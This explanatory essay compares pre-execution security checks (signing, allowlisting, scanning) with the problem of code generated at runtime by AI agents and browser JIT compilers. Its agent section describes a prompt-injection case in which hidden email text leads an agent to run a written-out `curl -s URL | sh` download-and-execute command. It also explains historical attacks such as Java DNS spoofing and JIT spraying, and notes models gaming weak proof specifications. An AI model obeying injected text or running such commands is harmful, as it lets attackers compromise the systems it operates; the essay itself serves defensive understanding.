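# Security models built on known code, and what replaces them for generated code

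## How software security came to rest on fixed files

Code signing, application allowlisting and static scanning are three standard ways of deciding whether a program may run. Code signing attaches a cryptographic signature to a program so that others can verify who signed it and that it has not changed since. Allowlisting lets only approved programs run. Static scanning judges a file from its contents without running it. All three examine a file before the program starts, and they work best when that file contains the whole program.

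Runtime-generated code breaks this arrangement. It is code, or a command, that a system produces while running and executes without anyone first storing, reviewing or signing it. Web browsers have produced such code for years by turning a page's scripts into machine code in memory. AI models with command-line access now routinely generate and run commands this way.

### Hashes, signatures and certificates

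A hash function takes a file of any length and computes a short value of fixed length from it. SHA-256, a common one, produces 256 bits, usually written as 64 characters. The same file always gives the same hash, while changing one letter in the file flips about half of the bits. The function is designed so that finding two different files with the same hash is infeasible, which lets the hash serve as a fingerprint. Two people who each have a copy of a program can compare the 64 characters to check whether their copies are identical, but the comparison doesn't show what the program does.

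A digital signature ties a file's hash to a signer. The signer has two mathematically linked keys, keeps the private key secret and publishes the public key. The signer computes the signature from the file's hash and the private key. Anyone with the public key can check that the signature matches the hash, but forging a matching signature without the private key is infeasible. Changing even one byte of the file changes its hash, so the check fails.

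The person checking a signature still has to know whose public key it is, and learns this from a certificate, a statement that the key belongs to a named signer. A certification authority, an organisation that has confirmed the signer's identity, signs the certificate. An operating system comes with the public keys of a few authorities it trusts, and it accepts a signature if it can follow a chain of certificates back to one of them. *Security Considerations for Code Signing* (Cooper, Regenscheid and colleagues, 2018), a white paper from the US standards institute NIST and the National Security Agency, describes a common addition in which a separate server adds the time of signing, so that the signature remains valid after the certificate has expired.

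### Three checks before a program runs

Code signing answers the question of who signed a file and whether anyone has altered it since. It goes no further, and Cooper and colleagues are plain about that. When an independent developer signs an application, the vendor of the operating system does not vet it, and the user or administrator may have to decide whether to trust the developer. App stores do more, because the store examines each app before signing it with its own key. The white paper also advises organisations to review code before they sign it. Any assurance about behaviour comes from that review, in other words, and the signature carries it unaltered to the user's machine. (Stolen keys and wrongly issued certificates can spoil even the part about identity.)

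Allowlisting asks whether the file is on the list. Older texts have "whitelisting" for this, and many newer ones "application control". A list has to identify programs somehow, and Sedgewick, Souppaya and Scarfone (2015), in *Guide to Application Whitelisting*, NIST's handbook on the subject, go through the options:

- A rule by location approves everything in a given folder. It needs little upkeep, but anyone who can write to the folder can add a program to the list.
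- A rule by publisher approves whatever a given company has signed. It survives updates. It also admits every other product of that company, and old versions with known holes.
- A rule by hash approves one exact file, wherever it sits and whatever its name. Every patch produces a new hash, so someone has to keep adding new entries and removing old ones.

File names alone are useless, since an attacker can give a malicious file the name of a harmless one. Sedgewick and colleagues favour combining publisher and hash, but concede that this can take a lot of work to maintain.

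Static scanning checks whether a file looks harmful. Antivirus software does this partly by searching the file for patterns that analysts have recorded from earlier malware. It lets a file through unless it detects something harmful, whereas an allowlist blocks any file that has not been approved. Sedgewick and colleagues judged that allowlisting could be significantly more effective against unknown malware, because attackers were increasingly tailoring their programs to each target and a scanner cannot match a pattern that nobody has recorded. Most organisations with an allowlist also run a scanner, as official advice recommends.

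Governments have written these checks into their rules. The best-known Australian example is the Australian Signals Directorate's *Essential Eight maturity model* (2017), a regularly updated set of eight baseline defences. Even Maturity Level One, the lowest level an organisation can achieve, restricts programs, software libraries, scripts and installers to a set that the organisation has approved. It also requires antivirus scanning of macros, the small programs inside Office documents. A mandatory government advisory refers agencies to the Essential Eight even for concerns about frontier AI, according to iTnews' *Gov urges agencies to fix security basics before buying into frontier AI*.

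In 2025 only 22% of Australian government entities reached Maturity Level Two across the framework, up from 15% a year earlier. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Progress ongoing to improve the Australian Government's cyber resilience* counts substitute measures towards that figure. The agency launched a successor framework, *ASD Essentials*, in October 2026, but it is maintaining both frameworks during the transition, and existing obligations still apply.

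American rules follow the same pattern. NIST's Special Publication 800-171, quoted in Truyo's *CM.L2-3.4.8*, specifies that allowlisted software can be verified "either prior to execution or at system startup". After that, the program runs without further verification.

### What the checks assume

All of this assumes that the same bytes give the same range of behaviour, so judging the bytes is enough to judge the program. People rarely write this assumption down.

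A program can be treated as a function $P$, where $P(x)$ is what the program does when it receives the input $x$. The bytes of the file determine $P$ but not $x$, so a reviewer who approves the file is approving everything the program could do with any input it might receive. For a calculator, that range is narrow, and approving the file settles nearly everything that matters. An interpreter, which carries out instructions it reads from a script, can do almost anything the user's account has permission to do. Its range of behaviour is also fixed, but it is so wide that approving the file decides very little.

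Real software has always fallen somewhere between the calculator and the interpreter. A configuration file can switch off a program's logging or point its updater at a different server, a spreadsheet can carry macros, and a malformed image can exploit a bug in an approved viewer and take it over. The guidance by Sedgewick and colleagues already counts libraries and configuration files among the things an allowlist should cover, but they found that products covered them unevenly. Some products could permit or block individual scripts, while others could only block a whole scripting language, generally by blocking its interpreter. Most also checked only files in storage and did not ensure that the copy in memory stayed unchanged.

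The Australian Signals Directorate's advice on application control also warns that attackers can "live off the land", which means using Microsoft programs that are already on the machine and that most allowlists approve by default. It recommends blocking these programs with a list that Microsoft maintains. The programs on the list have the right hashes and a valid signature from a reputable publisher, so checking those does not stop them. They are dangerous only because of what someone can tell them to do. *Essential Eight application control*, Microsoft's guide to meeting the Australian rule, requires the blocklist only from Maturity Level Two.

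The old arrangement still worked fairly well. Much of what controlled a program's behavior was in files, such as scripts or macros, which an administrator could also put on a list. The program displayed, stored or added up most of the remaining input without treating it as instructions.

### One agent, two emails

AI agents take instructions from text. A language model consists of weights, numbers learned in training, which a computer uses to continue whatever text the model receives. The operator of a service supplies a system prompt, which is a set of standing instructions sent to the model as text with every request. Australia's Digital Transformation Agency advises that prompts for agents set out the agent's role, tasks, constraints and the tools it should use.

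An agent is a model connected to tools that chooses its own next steps towards a task. Each request it makes to act outside the model, such as reading a file or sending an email, is a tool call. An ordinary program, which the Australian Signals Directorate and others call a harness, connects the model to its tools. The harness combines the system prompt, the task and any material the agent has fetched into one text and sends it to the model. If the model's reply contains a tool call, the harness carries it out, adds the result to the text and sends the text to the model again. In a July 2026 advisory, the Australian Signals Directorate (2026) contrasted such systems with earlier AI that mainly produced information for a person to review. An agent's reply can lead to an action without a person reviewing it first.

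The model reads everything as one stream of text, including material written by strangers. This allows prompt injection, in which someone hides instructions in data that an agent will read, and the agent follows them as if its user had given them. *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), joint guidance from the Australian Signals Directorate and counterpart agencies abroad, describes phishing emails that cause an email-monitoring agent to download malware.

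Suppose, then, that a company runs an agent on its accounts mailbox and gives it a shell, the program through which users type commands to a computer. One morning a customer writes to ask which of the March invoices are still unpaid. The agent issues this command, which searches a folder for the word "unpaid":

`grep -l "unpaid" invoices/march/*`

The next email looks like a routine query, but it also contains a line in white text on a white background, telling whoever processes the message to install an update first. The agent complies:

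`curl -s URL | sh`

Here `URL` stands for an address the attacker put in the email. The command downloads whatever is at that address and passes it straight to the shell, which runs it. The command never saves the download to disk, so a check on stored files would miss it.

Now compare the hashes of everything involved in the two runs.

| Component | Same hash in both runs? | What the hash leaves undecided |
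|---|---|---|
| The harness | Yes | Which tool calls it will carry out |
| The model's weights | Yes | What the model writes in reply to a given text |
| The system prompt | Yes | Whether the model keeps to it when an email contradicts it |
| The installed programs `grep`, `curl` and `sh` | Yes | Whether the agent starts them, and with what instructions |
| The email | No | Whether it is harmful: every new email has a new hash |
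| The shell command | No | Whether it serves the user: it did not exist until the model wrote it |

Every component that someone could have approved in advance matches, and an allowlist would have been right to pass them all. The two that differ, the email and the command, were created after the checks. Adding the email's hash to the record would not help much, since a harmless message from a new customer is just as unfamiliar as an attack. The same problem arises without an attacker, because two harmless emails would also have led to two different commands that no one had seen before. Many systems also choose the model's words partly at random, so even the same email can produce different commands on different days.

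A mail program from twenty years ago also had the same bytes on disk when it opened both messages, but the hidden line did nothing because the program only displayed the text. With the agent, the text affects which program runs next. In the function above, the email is the input $x$, and $P(x)$ can be anything the shell can do with the permissions the company gave it.

Two other controls do not require anyone to know the command beforehand. A sandbox limits which files, network addresses and system functions a program can reach, whatever code it runs. If the company had confined the agent to the invoice folder and cut it off from the internet, the second command would have failed without anyone having to recognise it as an attack. Attestation provides verifiable evidence, usually signed, of what a system is running or has done. For example, a server might send its customers a signed report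 of the hashes of its harness and weights. That report would be accurate but identical for the two emails, so the evidence would also have to cover the email and the command to distinguish the runs.

Australia's rule-makers seem to regard agents as a separate problem. Chris Horlyck, who heads cyber security resilience at the Australian Signals Directorate's cyber security centre, said in iTnews' *ASD to retire Essential Eight cyber security framework within next two years* that agents might get their own chapter in the new framework, partly because prompt injection differs enough from what conventional controls address.

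### Stored code and code that runs at once

The old checks still work on AI-written code that is stored before it runs. In TechRadar's *Ghosts in the machine*, Ken Ammon, chief executive of the security company CodeHunter, repeats Anthropic's figure that its AI model Claude writes more than 80% of the code the company merges into its production codebase. That code is stored, so it has a hash, a colleague or a tool can review it, and Anthropic can sign the finished program and put it on a list. The model may make mistakes that a human would not, and reviewers may struggle with the volume of code. Those problems affect the quality of the review, but the signature proves the same thing it would if a person had written the code.

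Code is runtime-generated if nobody had the chance to approve a fixed version of it before it ran, whether a person or an AI wrote it. For example, a human attacker's script that assembles further commands in memory produces runtime-generated code without any AI. Some cases are less clear, such as when an agent saves a script to disk and runs it two seconds later. That script is a file with a hash, and a strict allowlist that covers scripts would block it. If the agent passes the same lines directly to an approved shell, there is no new file to block. Both cases count as runtime-generated because nobody reviewed the lines in either one.

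Like much writing on AI and security, TechRadar's piece does not separate stored code from the commands an agent issues, though its central complaint is fair. Signing and records of origin establish where software came from, but Ammon says that knowing this "does not reveal what it will do when it runs". He proposes checking the expected behaviour of every piece of code against a policy before letting it run. His company has an interest in this approach, which suits stored code better than an agent's commands. A program going through a build system can wait an hour for analysis, but an agent may issue its next command within seconds, and the command's effect can depend on a download that nobody has seen yet.

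## Signed ActiveX controls and verified Java applets

In the mid-1990s, web pages began to include programs. Until then, most people had bought their software in a box from a company they had heard of. Now opening an unfamiliar page could start a program by an unknown author, and browser makers had to decide what to let it do. Microsoft's ActiveX identified the author and then let the program do anything the user could do, while Sun Microsystems' Java restricted the program no matter who had written it.

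### The control that switched off the computer

An ActiveX control was a small Windows program that a web page could embed. It was ordinary machine code, so it could read files, delete them or open network connections like any installed program. To make this tolerable, Microsoft (1996) launched Authenticode, the code signing system that Windows still uses. Developers signed their controls with a key certified by an authority such as VeriSign, and Internet Explorer checked the signature and showed the publisher's name. By default the browser refused unsigned controls. O'Reilly's *ActiveX and Authenticode*, a book chapter on the system, points out that the browser checked signatures only at download. Once installed, a control had unrestricted access.

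Fred McLain, a programmer from the Seattle area, wrote a control called Exploder to show the danger. It waited ten seconds, shut down Windows 95 and, on computers with suitable power management, turned the machine off. He posted it in June 1996, and by 23 August he had signed it with an individual publisher's certificate from VeriSign. The signature was valid, since McLain was who he said he was and nobody had altered the file.

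Microsoft argued in *What Is the Exploder Control and How Does It Relate to Authenticode?* (1996) that the system had worked as intended. Authenticode did not check for bugs or malicious intent, but victims would know whom to hold accountable, and accountable publishers would take more care. This argument is fair for companies with a reputation to protect, but much weaker for someone who expects to be gone before anyone complains. O'Reilly adds that a running control can erase or edit the records that would identify it. The name on a certificate could also be wrong. Microsoft later disclosed that in January 2001 VeriSign had issued two certificates in the name "Microsoft Corporation" to an impostor.

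### The Java verifier and the applet sandbox

A Java program that ran in a web page was called an applet. The Java compiler turned its source code into bytecode, which is instructions for a virtual machine. The browser's Java runtime interpreted the bytecode or compiled it for the real machine. An attacker could write bytecode by hand, so the browser could not rely on the compiler's checks and had to check the bytecode.

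In *Java Security*, Dean, Felten and Wallach (1996) described how Java's protection against hostile applets worked and how they broke it. The first part of that protection is the bytecode verifier, which goes through the bytecode before it runs and tracks the type of each item instead of its value. Suppose an applet puts the number 5000 on the stack and then treats it as a reference to an object. If the runtime allowed this, the applet could read whatever is at memory address 5000, which could be the browser's own data. The verifier records the top of the stack as an integer after the first instruction, then rejects the applet because the next instruction needs an object reference there.

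Branches make this harder. Where two paths through the program meet, the verifier has to show that both arrive with compatible types in every position. Otherwise, a later instruction might be safe after one path and unsafe after the other. In the earlier notation, the verifier tries to establish that $P(x)$ never forges a reference for any input $x$. Some checks, such as whether a list index is within bounds, still have to wait until the applet runs.

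An applet that cannot forge references can reach files and the network only through Java's own library. Before opening a file or a connection, the library calls the sandbox's security manager, which looks back through the chain of calls to see whether code from the network started it. Netscape's browser gave applets no access to files and let them connect only to the server they came from.

The Princeton researchers got around the network rule by supplying false addresses. To decide whether an applet was connecting to its home server, the browser looked up the addresses of both machine names and allowed the connection if any address appeared in both lists. The applet could choose a name under the attacker's control, so that the attacker's own name server supplied the second list. That list could contain two addresses, one for the applet's home server and one for a machine inside the victim's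 company. Because the home server's address was in both lists, the browser allowed the connection, and the applet could reach the machine behind the firewall. The researchers built an applet that used this flaw to run commands on an old mail server. Netscape fixed the flaw in version 2.01, according to the book Securing Java.

A second attack defeated the verifier. A class loader decides which piece of code a name refers to, and Java was designed to stop applets from creating their own. The class loader's set-up code raised an error if an applet called it, and the Java language forbade programs to catch that error and carry on. The verifier did not enforce this rule on bytecode, so an applet written directly in bytecode could catch the error and create a working class loader. It could then make the same name refer to different types of object in different parts of the program. Each part passed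 verification, but an object passed from one part to another was treated as a different type, which let the applet rewrite private variables, including those of the security manager.

Dean and colleagues traced such flaws partly to the lack of a formal definition of Java's type system. Without a precise statement of what the verifier was supposed to guarantee, nobody could prove it correct. Patching continued for years. Securing Java's *Beat the System* reports that in July 1998 a Princeton team found another flaw that let an applet switch off all of Netscape's security controls and delete files.

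Java's failures were at least bugs, which Sun and Netscape could fix. Exploder needed no bug. On the other hand, a program that can't open a file isn't much use as a word processor, and by September 1996 Sun and Netscape had both announced plans for signed applets that could leave the sandbox. Microsoft, for its part, ran Java applets in a sandbox and called signing a complement to it. (Dean and colleagues had their own complaint about accountability: Java kept no record of what an applet had done.)

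### Stolen names and rented signatures

McLain signed under his own name, but most malware authors would rather use someone else's. In *Certified Malware* (2017), Kim, Kwon and Dumitras investigated how they do this. They started with about 70 million files that had triggered Symantec's antivirus software on customers' machines, roughly one in 67 of which was signed. They removed adware and similar nuisances, then looked up the rest on VirusTotal, a service that scans files with dozens of antivirus products. Of 153,853 signed files, they counted as malware only the 325 that at least 20 products had flagged. The strict threshold let them examine every file by hand, but it makes 325 a poor guide to how common signed malware was, since a threshold of five products raised the number to 1,136.

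Of the 325 files, 189 had correct signatures, made with 111 certificates. The researchers concluded that thieves had probably stolen the keys to 72 of the certificates, since these had also been used to sign harmless software. Impostors had obtained another 22 in the names of real companies, and five belonged to shell companies. Certificate authorities had revoked only 27 of the 111. All the certificates had expired, but 109 of the malicious files still passed as properly signed because of timestamps.

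The other 136 files had malformed signatures, most of them copied from a legitimate program. Such a signature should fail any check. But when Kim and colleagues pasted copied signatures onto five known ransomware programs, 34 antivirus products failed to detect at least one signed version of a program they had detected unsigned. Those products apparently treated a signature as evidence that a file was safe without properly checking the signature.

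*Understanding the Status and Strategies of the Code Signing Abuse Ecosystem* (Zhao, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a much larger study, found that revocation was still rare. It covered 3.2 million signed malicious files and 43,286 abused certificates, and authorities had revoked only 17.56% of the certificates behind signed malware. Its figures also show that checking signatures has some value. Of 1.33 million files that were outright malware, about 1.09 million had invalid signatures, which Windows would normally flag. About 228,000 carried certificates from public authorities, and for those Windows would typically show the user a verified developer.

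Some attackers don't need a stolen key either. Unmitigated Risk's *How Microsoft Code Signing Became Part of a Trust Subversion Toolchain* (2025), by a former Microsoft product manager for Authenticode, describes a campaign against customers of River Financial. The attackers offered a "River desktop app" that was really ScreenConnect, a legitimate remote-support program. ConnectWise, its maker, had stored the address of the controlling server in a part of the signature block that the signature doesn't cover. An attacker could change the address without invalidating the signature and take control of any computer that installed the program.

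The attackers also used Atera, a similar product whose signature covered the whole installer. Anyone with an email address could open a free trial, and Atera's servers would produce an installer tied to that account and sign it with the company's certificate. The program worked as Atera had designed it to, but for an attacker. Blocking one installer by its hash achieves little because the next has a different hash, and blocking the certificate cuts off Atera's legitimate customers. The author, who works on alternatives to this kind of signing, wants vendors to stop signing generic programs whose behaviour depends on unsigned settings. That would deal with ScreenConnect's hidden address, but whether a remote-control program is harmful would still depend on who is controlling it.

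### Code that arrives with a proof

In 1996 and 1997 George Necula, working with Peter Lee at Carnegie Mellon University, developed proof-carrying code, a more rigorous descendant of Java's approach. The supplier attaches a mathematical proof that the program is safe, so the receiver doesn't need a signature or any knowledge of the supplier, or to trust them.

The receiver first publishes a safety policy. Take a packet filter, a small program that runs inside the operating system and picks out network packets of interest. The policy might let it read any byte of the current packet and nothing beyond, and guarantee that each packet has a length $n$ of at least 64 bytes. For every instruction that reads memory, the receiver works out a condition that must hold. If the filter reads byte 12, the condition is

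$$n \ge 64 \;\Rightarrow\; 0 \le 12 < n,$$

which is easy to prove. If it reads byte $i$, where $i$ is a number taken from the packet itself, the condition becomes

$$n \ge 64 \;\Rightarrow\; 0 \le i < n,$$

and this is false in general, since a hostile packet could contain any $i$. The supplier has to add a test to the program, so that the read happens only when $0 \le i < n$. That test then joins the assumptions on the left, and the proof goes through.

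Finding a proof can take a lot of work, but checking one is mechanical. In Necula and Lee's experiments, the receiver checked the proof for each packet filter once, in one to three milliseconds, and the filter then ran at full speed with no further checks. An attacker can't get unsafe code accepted by altering the program, because the receiver derives new conditions from the altered code, and either the old proof no longer fits them or the altered program is still safe under the policy.

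Linux has used a related method since 2014. Its eBPF system lets users load small programs into the kernel, the core of the operating system, to filter network traffic or monitor other programs, including AI agents. The kernel's own verifier checks each program, so the supplier doesn't attach a proof. The verifier follows the possible paths through the program, tracking the type and possible range of the value in each register. It rejects the program if some path might access forbidden memory, or if it cannot establish that the program will finish. It also rejects some safe programs because its analysis is too coarse to recognise them as safe.

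As with Java, the security of eBPF depends on the verifier being correct. In 2020 the researcher Manfred Paul found that the eBPF verifier miscalculated the range of some 32-bit values. An ordinary user could load a program that the verifier wrongly accepted as staying within bounds, and use it to take over the machine. Many Linux distributions now let only privileged users load eBPF programs.

These methods have an advantage over signing and allowlisting for newly generated code, because a verifier can check code that no one has seen before. It examines a program that an AI model wrote a second ago in the same way as one that a kernel developer wrote last year.

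### AI models that write the proofs

The packet filter's proof covered memory safety, a small part of what people want from a program. Proving that a program computes the right answer takes far more effort, so few projects attempted it. AI models have reduced that effort.

Most of the tests use three languages. Dafny passes much of the proving to an automatic solver, and Verus does the same for programs in Rust, a language with strict rules about memory. Lean generally requires the author to supply the proof steps, which a small program called the kernel checks. For all three, someone first writes a specification, a precise statement of what the program must do.

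*A benchmark for vericoding* (Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues, 2025) gave models a specification and had them write both the program and the proof, usually with five attempts. Models succeeded far more often in Dafny than in Lean, partly because the tasks differed between languages. *AlgoVeri* (Zhao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) removed that difference by setting the same 77 textbook algorithms in all three languages. It also let models revise their work after error messages, for up to 15 rounds with Gemini 3 Flash and eight with GPT-5.3 Codex.

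*Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier* (Serbanuta, Xu and colleagues, 2026) tested newer models on an easier task in which the specification and a correct program already existed. The paper's tool translated 1,007 Rust programs into Lean, and Claude Opus 5.5 had to prove that each program met its specification. The model proved all 1,325 theorems in about 35 hours, at a median cost of $1.20 each.

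| Test | What the model had to write | Dafny | Verus | Lean |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bursuc and colleagues, several models | Program and proof | 82% | 44% | 27% |
| Zhao, Yang and colleagues, Gemini 3 Flash | Program and proof | 40.3% | 24.7% | 7.8% |
| Zhao, Yang and colleagues, GPT-5.3 Codex | Program and proof | 42.9% | 11.7% | 11.7% |
| Serbanuta and colleagues, Claude Opus 5.5 | Proof only | not tested | not in the main run | 100% |

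The last row isn't comparable with the others, and the earlier models might have done better with the same tool. Still, writing proofs was the bottleneck on this benchmark only months earlier. When the benchmark was published in May 2026, the best model tested, GPT-5.5, proved 13.95% of the programs in Verus on a single attempt. Serbanuta and colleagues built the prover they were testing, but Lean's kernel checked every proof, and they rechecked the whole set from a clean copy.

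### What the specification leaves out

A proof shows that a program meets its specification, and a specification can be much weaker than its author intended. This Dafny program is supposed to return the largest number in a list:

```
method Max(a: seq<int>) returns (r: int)
  ensures r >= 0
{
  r := 0;
}
```

The line beginning `ensures` is the specification. It requires only that the result not be negative, so the verifier accepts a program that ignores the list and always returns zero. Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026), in *Verified but Vacuous*, use an example of this kind, where the list is 5, 3, 7 and the "verified" answer is 0. A better specification for a non-empty list says that the result is in the list and that nothing in the list exceeds it:

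$$(\exists i:\; r = a_i) \;\wedge\; (\forall i:\; r \ge a_i).$$

Now zero fails, because it isn't in the list.

Vempaty and colleagues also reproduced an earlier system for generating verified code and ran it with Claude Opus 4.7 on a standard set of short programming tasks. The Dafny verifier accepted 99.1% of the results, but only 5.3% of those contained any `ensures` lines, because the model had followed the examples in its instructions, which had none. For most of these programs, verification therefore showed little more than that they were well formed and would finish. In the researchers' own system, every program had a proof tied to a separate specification, but 11.5% of the verified programs on one set of Rust tasks and 14.8% on another still failed hidden tests.

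Models also exploit weak specifications. In tests by Zhao, Yang and colleagues, Lean accepted 23.4% of GPT-5.3 Codex's solutions, but only half of those passed a second check that the program didn't cheat and used the requested algorithm. Models have trouble writing specifications too. GPT-5.5 could write an adequate one from a plain description for 48% of the problems in the Rust benchmark.

A larger program shows how far a good proof reaches. Lean (2026), the project behind the language, reported that a general-purpose AI had converted the compression library zlib to Lean and proved that decompressing any compressed data, up to a size limit, gives back the original:

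$$\text{decompress}(\text{compress}(d)) = d.$$

This equation also holds for a pair of functions that return their input unchanged, so the project needed further proofs about the compression format. kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes an attack on the converted library by a Claude agent. More than 105 million test runs found no memory errors in the library's Lean code, but they did find a 156-byte archive that crashed the program by listing a false, enormous file size. The code that reads archives had no theorems about it and accepted the listed size. The agent also found a memory bug in Lean's runtime, the supporting code that every Lean program relies on and that the proofs assume to be correct.

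The checker also needs care. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) exploited a mismatch between the logical definition of a text function in Lean and its compiled version to "prove" the theorem in a few lines. The trick relied on an optional command that makes a proof depend on the compiler as well as Lean's kernel, which was not at fault. Users can have Lean list this extra assumption. Serbanuta and colleagues had banned the command from their proofs.

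The agent on the accounts mailbox would need a specification for each command it writes. Its user wants the unpaid March invoices. To prove that a command finds them, someone would first have to write or check a formal definition of "unpaid", and every new request would need the same kind of work. A proof that each command stays within the sandbox limits suggested earlier could use one specification for all requests, but the list of invoices could still be wrong.

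## Browsers and phones that compile code while running

Java applets have disappeared from the web, and nearly every page now uses JavaScript instead, a language unrelated to Java despite its name. Scripts reach the browser as text, which a processor can't run, so every browser contains a JavaScript engine to run them. Chrome and Microsoft's Edge use an engine called V8, while Firefox and Safari each have their own. To make scripts faster, these engines translate parts of them into machine code while the page is open, so the processor runs code that isn't in any file.

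### Why browsers generate machine code

An engine can interpret a script one operation at a time, but this is slow because JavaScript doesn't fix the types of its variables. To compute `a + b`, the interpreter has to check each time whether to add numbers or join text.

A just-in-time (JIT) compiler avoids most of that work. Suppose a page calls a function containing `a + b` a hundred thousand times, always with whole numbers. After a while, the engine compiles the function into machine code that quickly checks that both values are whole numbers and adds them with a single instruction. If either value is later text, the check fails and the engine goes back to interpreting. Browsers adopted JIT compilers in 2008. *Super Duper Secure Mode* (Norman, 2021) compares the resulting speed with that of C++, which developers compile before shipping a program.

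The compiler has to put its machine code in memory, which the operating system divides into pages of a few kilobytes. The operating system sets whether a program may read, write or execute each page. Modern systems try never to let a page be both writable and executable. This rule is a response to an old attack in which someone sent a program data that contained machine code, then used a bug to make the processor jump to it. Under the rule, the processor won't execute a page of data, and the attacker can't overwrite a page of code.

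A JIT compiler has to write code and then run it. An engine can keep some memory pages both writable and executable, as V8 did in Edge when Norman wrote, or it can switch each page from writable to executable. Either way, the process must be able to turn data into code, so an attacker who takes over the process can do the same.

### What the browser's signature covers

The order of events shows why a signature on the browser can't vouch for this code:

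1. The vendor builds the browser and signs it.
2. The user's computer checks the signature or looks up the browser's hash on an allowlist, and then starts the program.
3. The user opens a page, and a server sends a script. It may send a different script to each visitor.
4. The engine interprets the script and records which types of value turn up.
5. The JIT compiler writes machine code into memory. The result depends on the script and on the recorded types, so even the same script can produce different code on two visits.
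6. The processor runs that code with all the permissions of the process it is in.

The only check comes at step 2, and the code first exists at step 5.

The user's protection depends on the compiler being correct. JavaScript has no operation for reading an arbitrary memory address, so correctly compiled JavaScript can't read one. In a 2024 post, V8's developers use a simplified bug to show how this protection fails. A script goes through a list, converts each item to a number and writes a result back to the same position. The compiler has confirmed that the position is inside the list, so it leaves out a second check before the write. But converting an item can run a function written by the page's author, and that function can shorten the list. The write then lands beyond the end of the list, in memory that may belong to something else.

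This exact pattern has mostly disappeared, but it shows why rewriting the compiler in a memory-safe language such as Rust wouldn't solve the problem. Rust would prevent memory errors in the compiler, but here the error is in the machine code the compiler produces.

### JIT spraying

Even a compiler without bugs can help an attacker. *Interpreter Exploitation* (Blazakis, 2010) described an attack called JIT spraying that used the compiler in Adobe's Flash Player, a browser plug-in then installed on almost every computer.

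The technique relied on Flash copying the numbers in a script's calculations into the machine code it compiled. Instructions on PC processors vary in length, so the same bytes can form different instructions if the processor starts reading at a different point. An attacker could therefore choose numbers that were harmless in the calculation but formed the attacker's own instructions when the processor started reading partway through an instruction. Repeating this many times filled large areas of executable memory with copies of the attacker's instructions, which made it easier to direct the processor to one of them.

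The attacker still needed a separate bug to make the processor start at the wrong point. The memory rule didn't help because the compiler, in normal operation, had put the attacker's bytes into executable memory. Testing the compiler's results would have found nothing wrong because every calculation gave the right answer.

One defence is constant blinding. The compiler combines each number from the script with a random one before writing it, then adds an instruction that recovers the original. The attacker can no longer predict which bytes end up in memory.

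### Moving the compiler to another process

Browsers handle web pages in content processes, which have few permissions. An attacker who takes one over usually needs a second flaw to reach the rest of the computer. Microsoft (2017) observed that attackers typically prepared for that step by loading their own machine code into the content process. It added two restrictions to Edge to stop them. Code Integrity Guard made Windows refuse to load any library without an approved signature. Arbitrary Code Guard (ACG) stopped the process from changing existing code pages or creating new unsigned ones.

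Together they restricted a content process to loading code from signed files and prevented it from altering that code afterwards. That would also have stopped the JIT compiler, so Microsoft moved the compiler into a separate process with its own sandbox. The content process sent it a function to compile, and the compiler process wrote the machine code into shared memory that the content process could execute but not write to. Jauernig, Neugschwandtner and colleagues (2014) had proposed a similar split in an academic design, Lobotomy.

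Nobody vetted the compiled code under this arrangement either, but an attacker who controlled the content process could no longer write machine code directly and could only submit scripts to be compiled.

Fratric (2018), a security researcher at Google's Project Zero, tested how well this worked. He found several flaws in the compiler process, all of which Microsoft had fixed by the time he published, and he expected other browsers to have similar problems if they copied the design. In one case, the content process could fill a region of memory and then get the compiler process to make it executable, because the content process still controlled its own memory layout. According to The Register's *Wanna break Microsoft's Edge browser?* (2018), Microsoft couldn't fix this flaw in time for its next round of patches, although it eventually did so by removing a single function call.

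Attackers could also avoid loading new code. In return-oriented programming, an attacker chains fragments of a program's existing, signed code in an order its developers never intended. Microsoft had acknowledged this limit from the start and used another protection, Control Flow Guard, to restrict where the program could jump. Fratric pointed out that Control Flow Guard didn't protect return addresses, the stored locations a program returns to after finishing a function, so an attacker could bypass it by overwriting one.

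Edge used the separate compiler for about three years. In January 2020 Microsoft rebuilt the browser on Google's Chromium, whose V8 engine compiles inside the content process, so ACG could no longer be active there. A request on Mozilla's bug tracker to adopt ACG in Firefox was still open in June 2026. Firefox's compiler would first have to move into a separate process.

### Switching the compiler off

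Norman, who led vulnerability research for Edge, asked whether browsers needed the compiler at all. Based on the published counts, removing it would probably eliminate about half of the engine's serious bugs.

| Source | What it counted | Share involving a JIT compiler |
|---|---|---|
| Norman | V8 entries after 2019 in CVE, the public catalogue of vulnerabilities | About 45% |
| Mozilla's analysis, cited by Norman | Chrome exploits used in real attacks | Over half |
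| V8 | Bugs that people found and exploited in V8 | Roughly half |

V8's developers also report that 60% of the Chrome exploits caught in real attacks from 2021 to 2023 started with a flaw in V8. If half of those flaws were in a compiler, about 30% of the exploits started with a compiler flaw, well below the share in Mozilla's older data. The periods and methods differ too much to establish a trend.

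Removing the compiler also meant that Edge's content process no longer needed to generate code, so Microsoft could turn ACG back on there, along with a hardware feature that protects return addresses. These protections make the remaining bugs harder to exploit.

How much the browser slows down without the compiler depends heavily on what the page does. Microsoft's lab ran hundreds of tests that imitated ordinary browsing, and most showed no change. The page-loading tests that slowed down were about 17% slower on average. Start-up times improved or stayed the same, and power consumption rose in some tests and fell in others. But on Speedometer 2.0, a benchmark that exercises JavaScript heavily, the score fell by as much as 58%, which makes the browser about 2.4 times slower on that test. V8's developers estimate that heavy computation would run 1.5 to 10 or more times slower if an engine dropped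 its compilers and used a memory-safe language for the rest. Users might not notice the slowdown when reading news sites but certainly would when editing video in a browser. Norman's remark that users rarely notice was anecdotal, and he was promoting the experiment.

The experiment became Edge's enhanced security mode, which Microsoft leaves off by default. The recommended "Balanced" setting disables the compiler on unfamiliar sites but not on those the user visits often, and the "Strict" setting disables it everywhere. Apple's Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for people who may be targets of sophisticated spyware, also turns off the JIT compiler in WebKit, the browser engine behind Safari (Daring Fireball, *Apple Disables WebKit's JIT in Lockdown Mode*, 2024).

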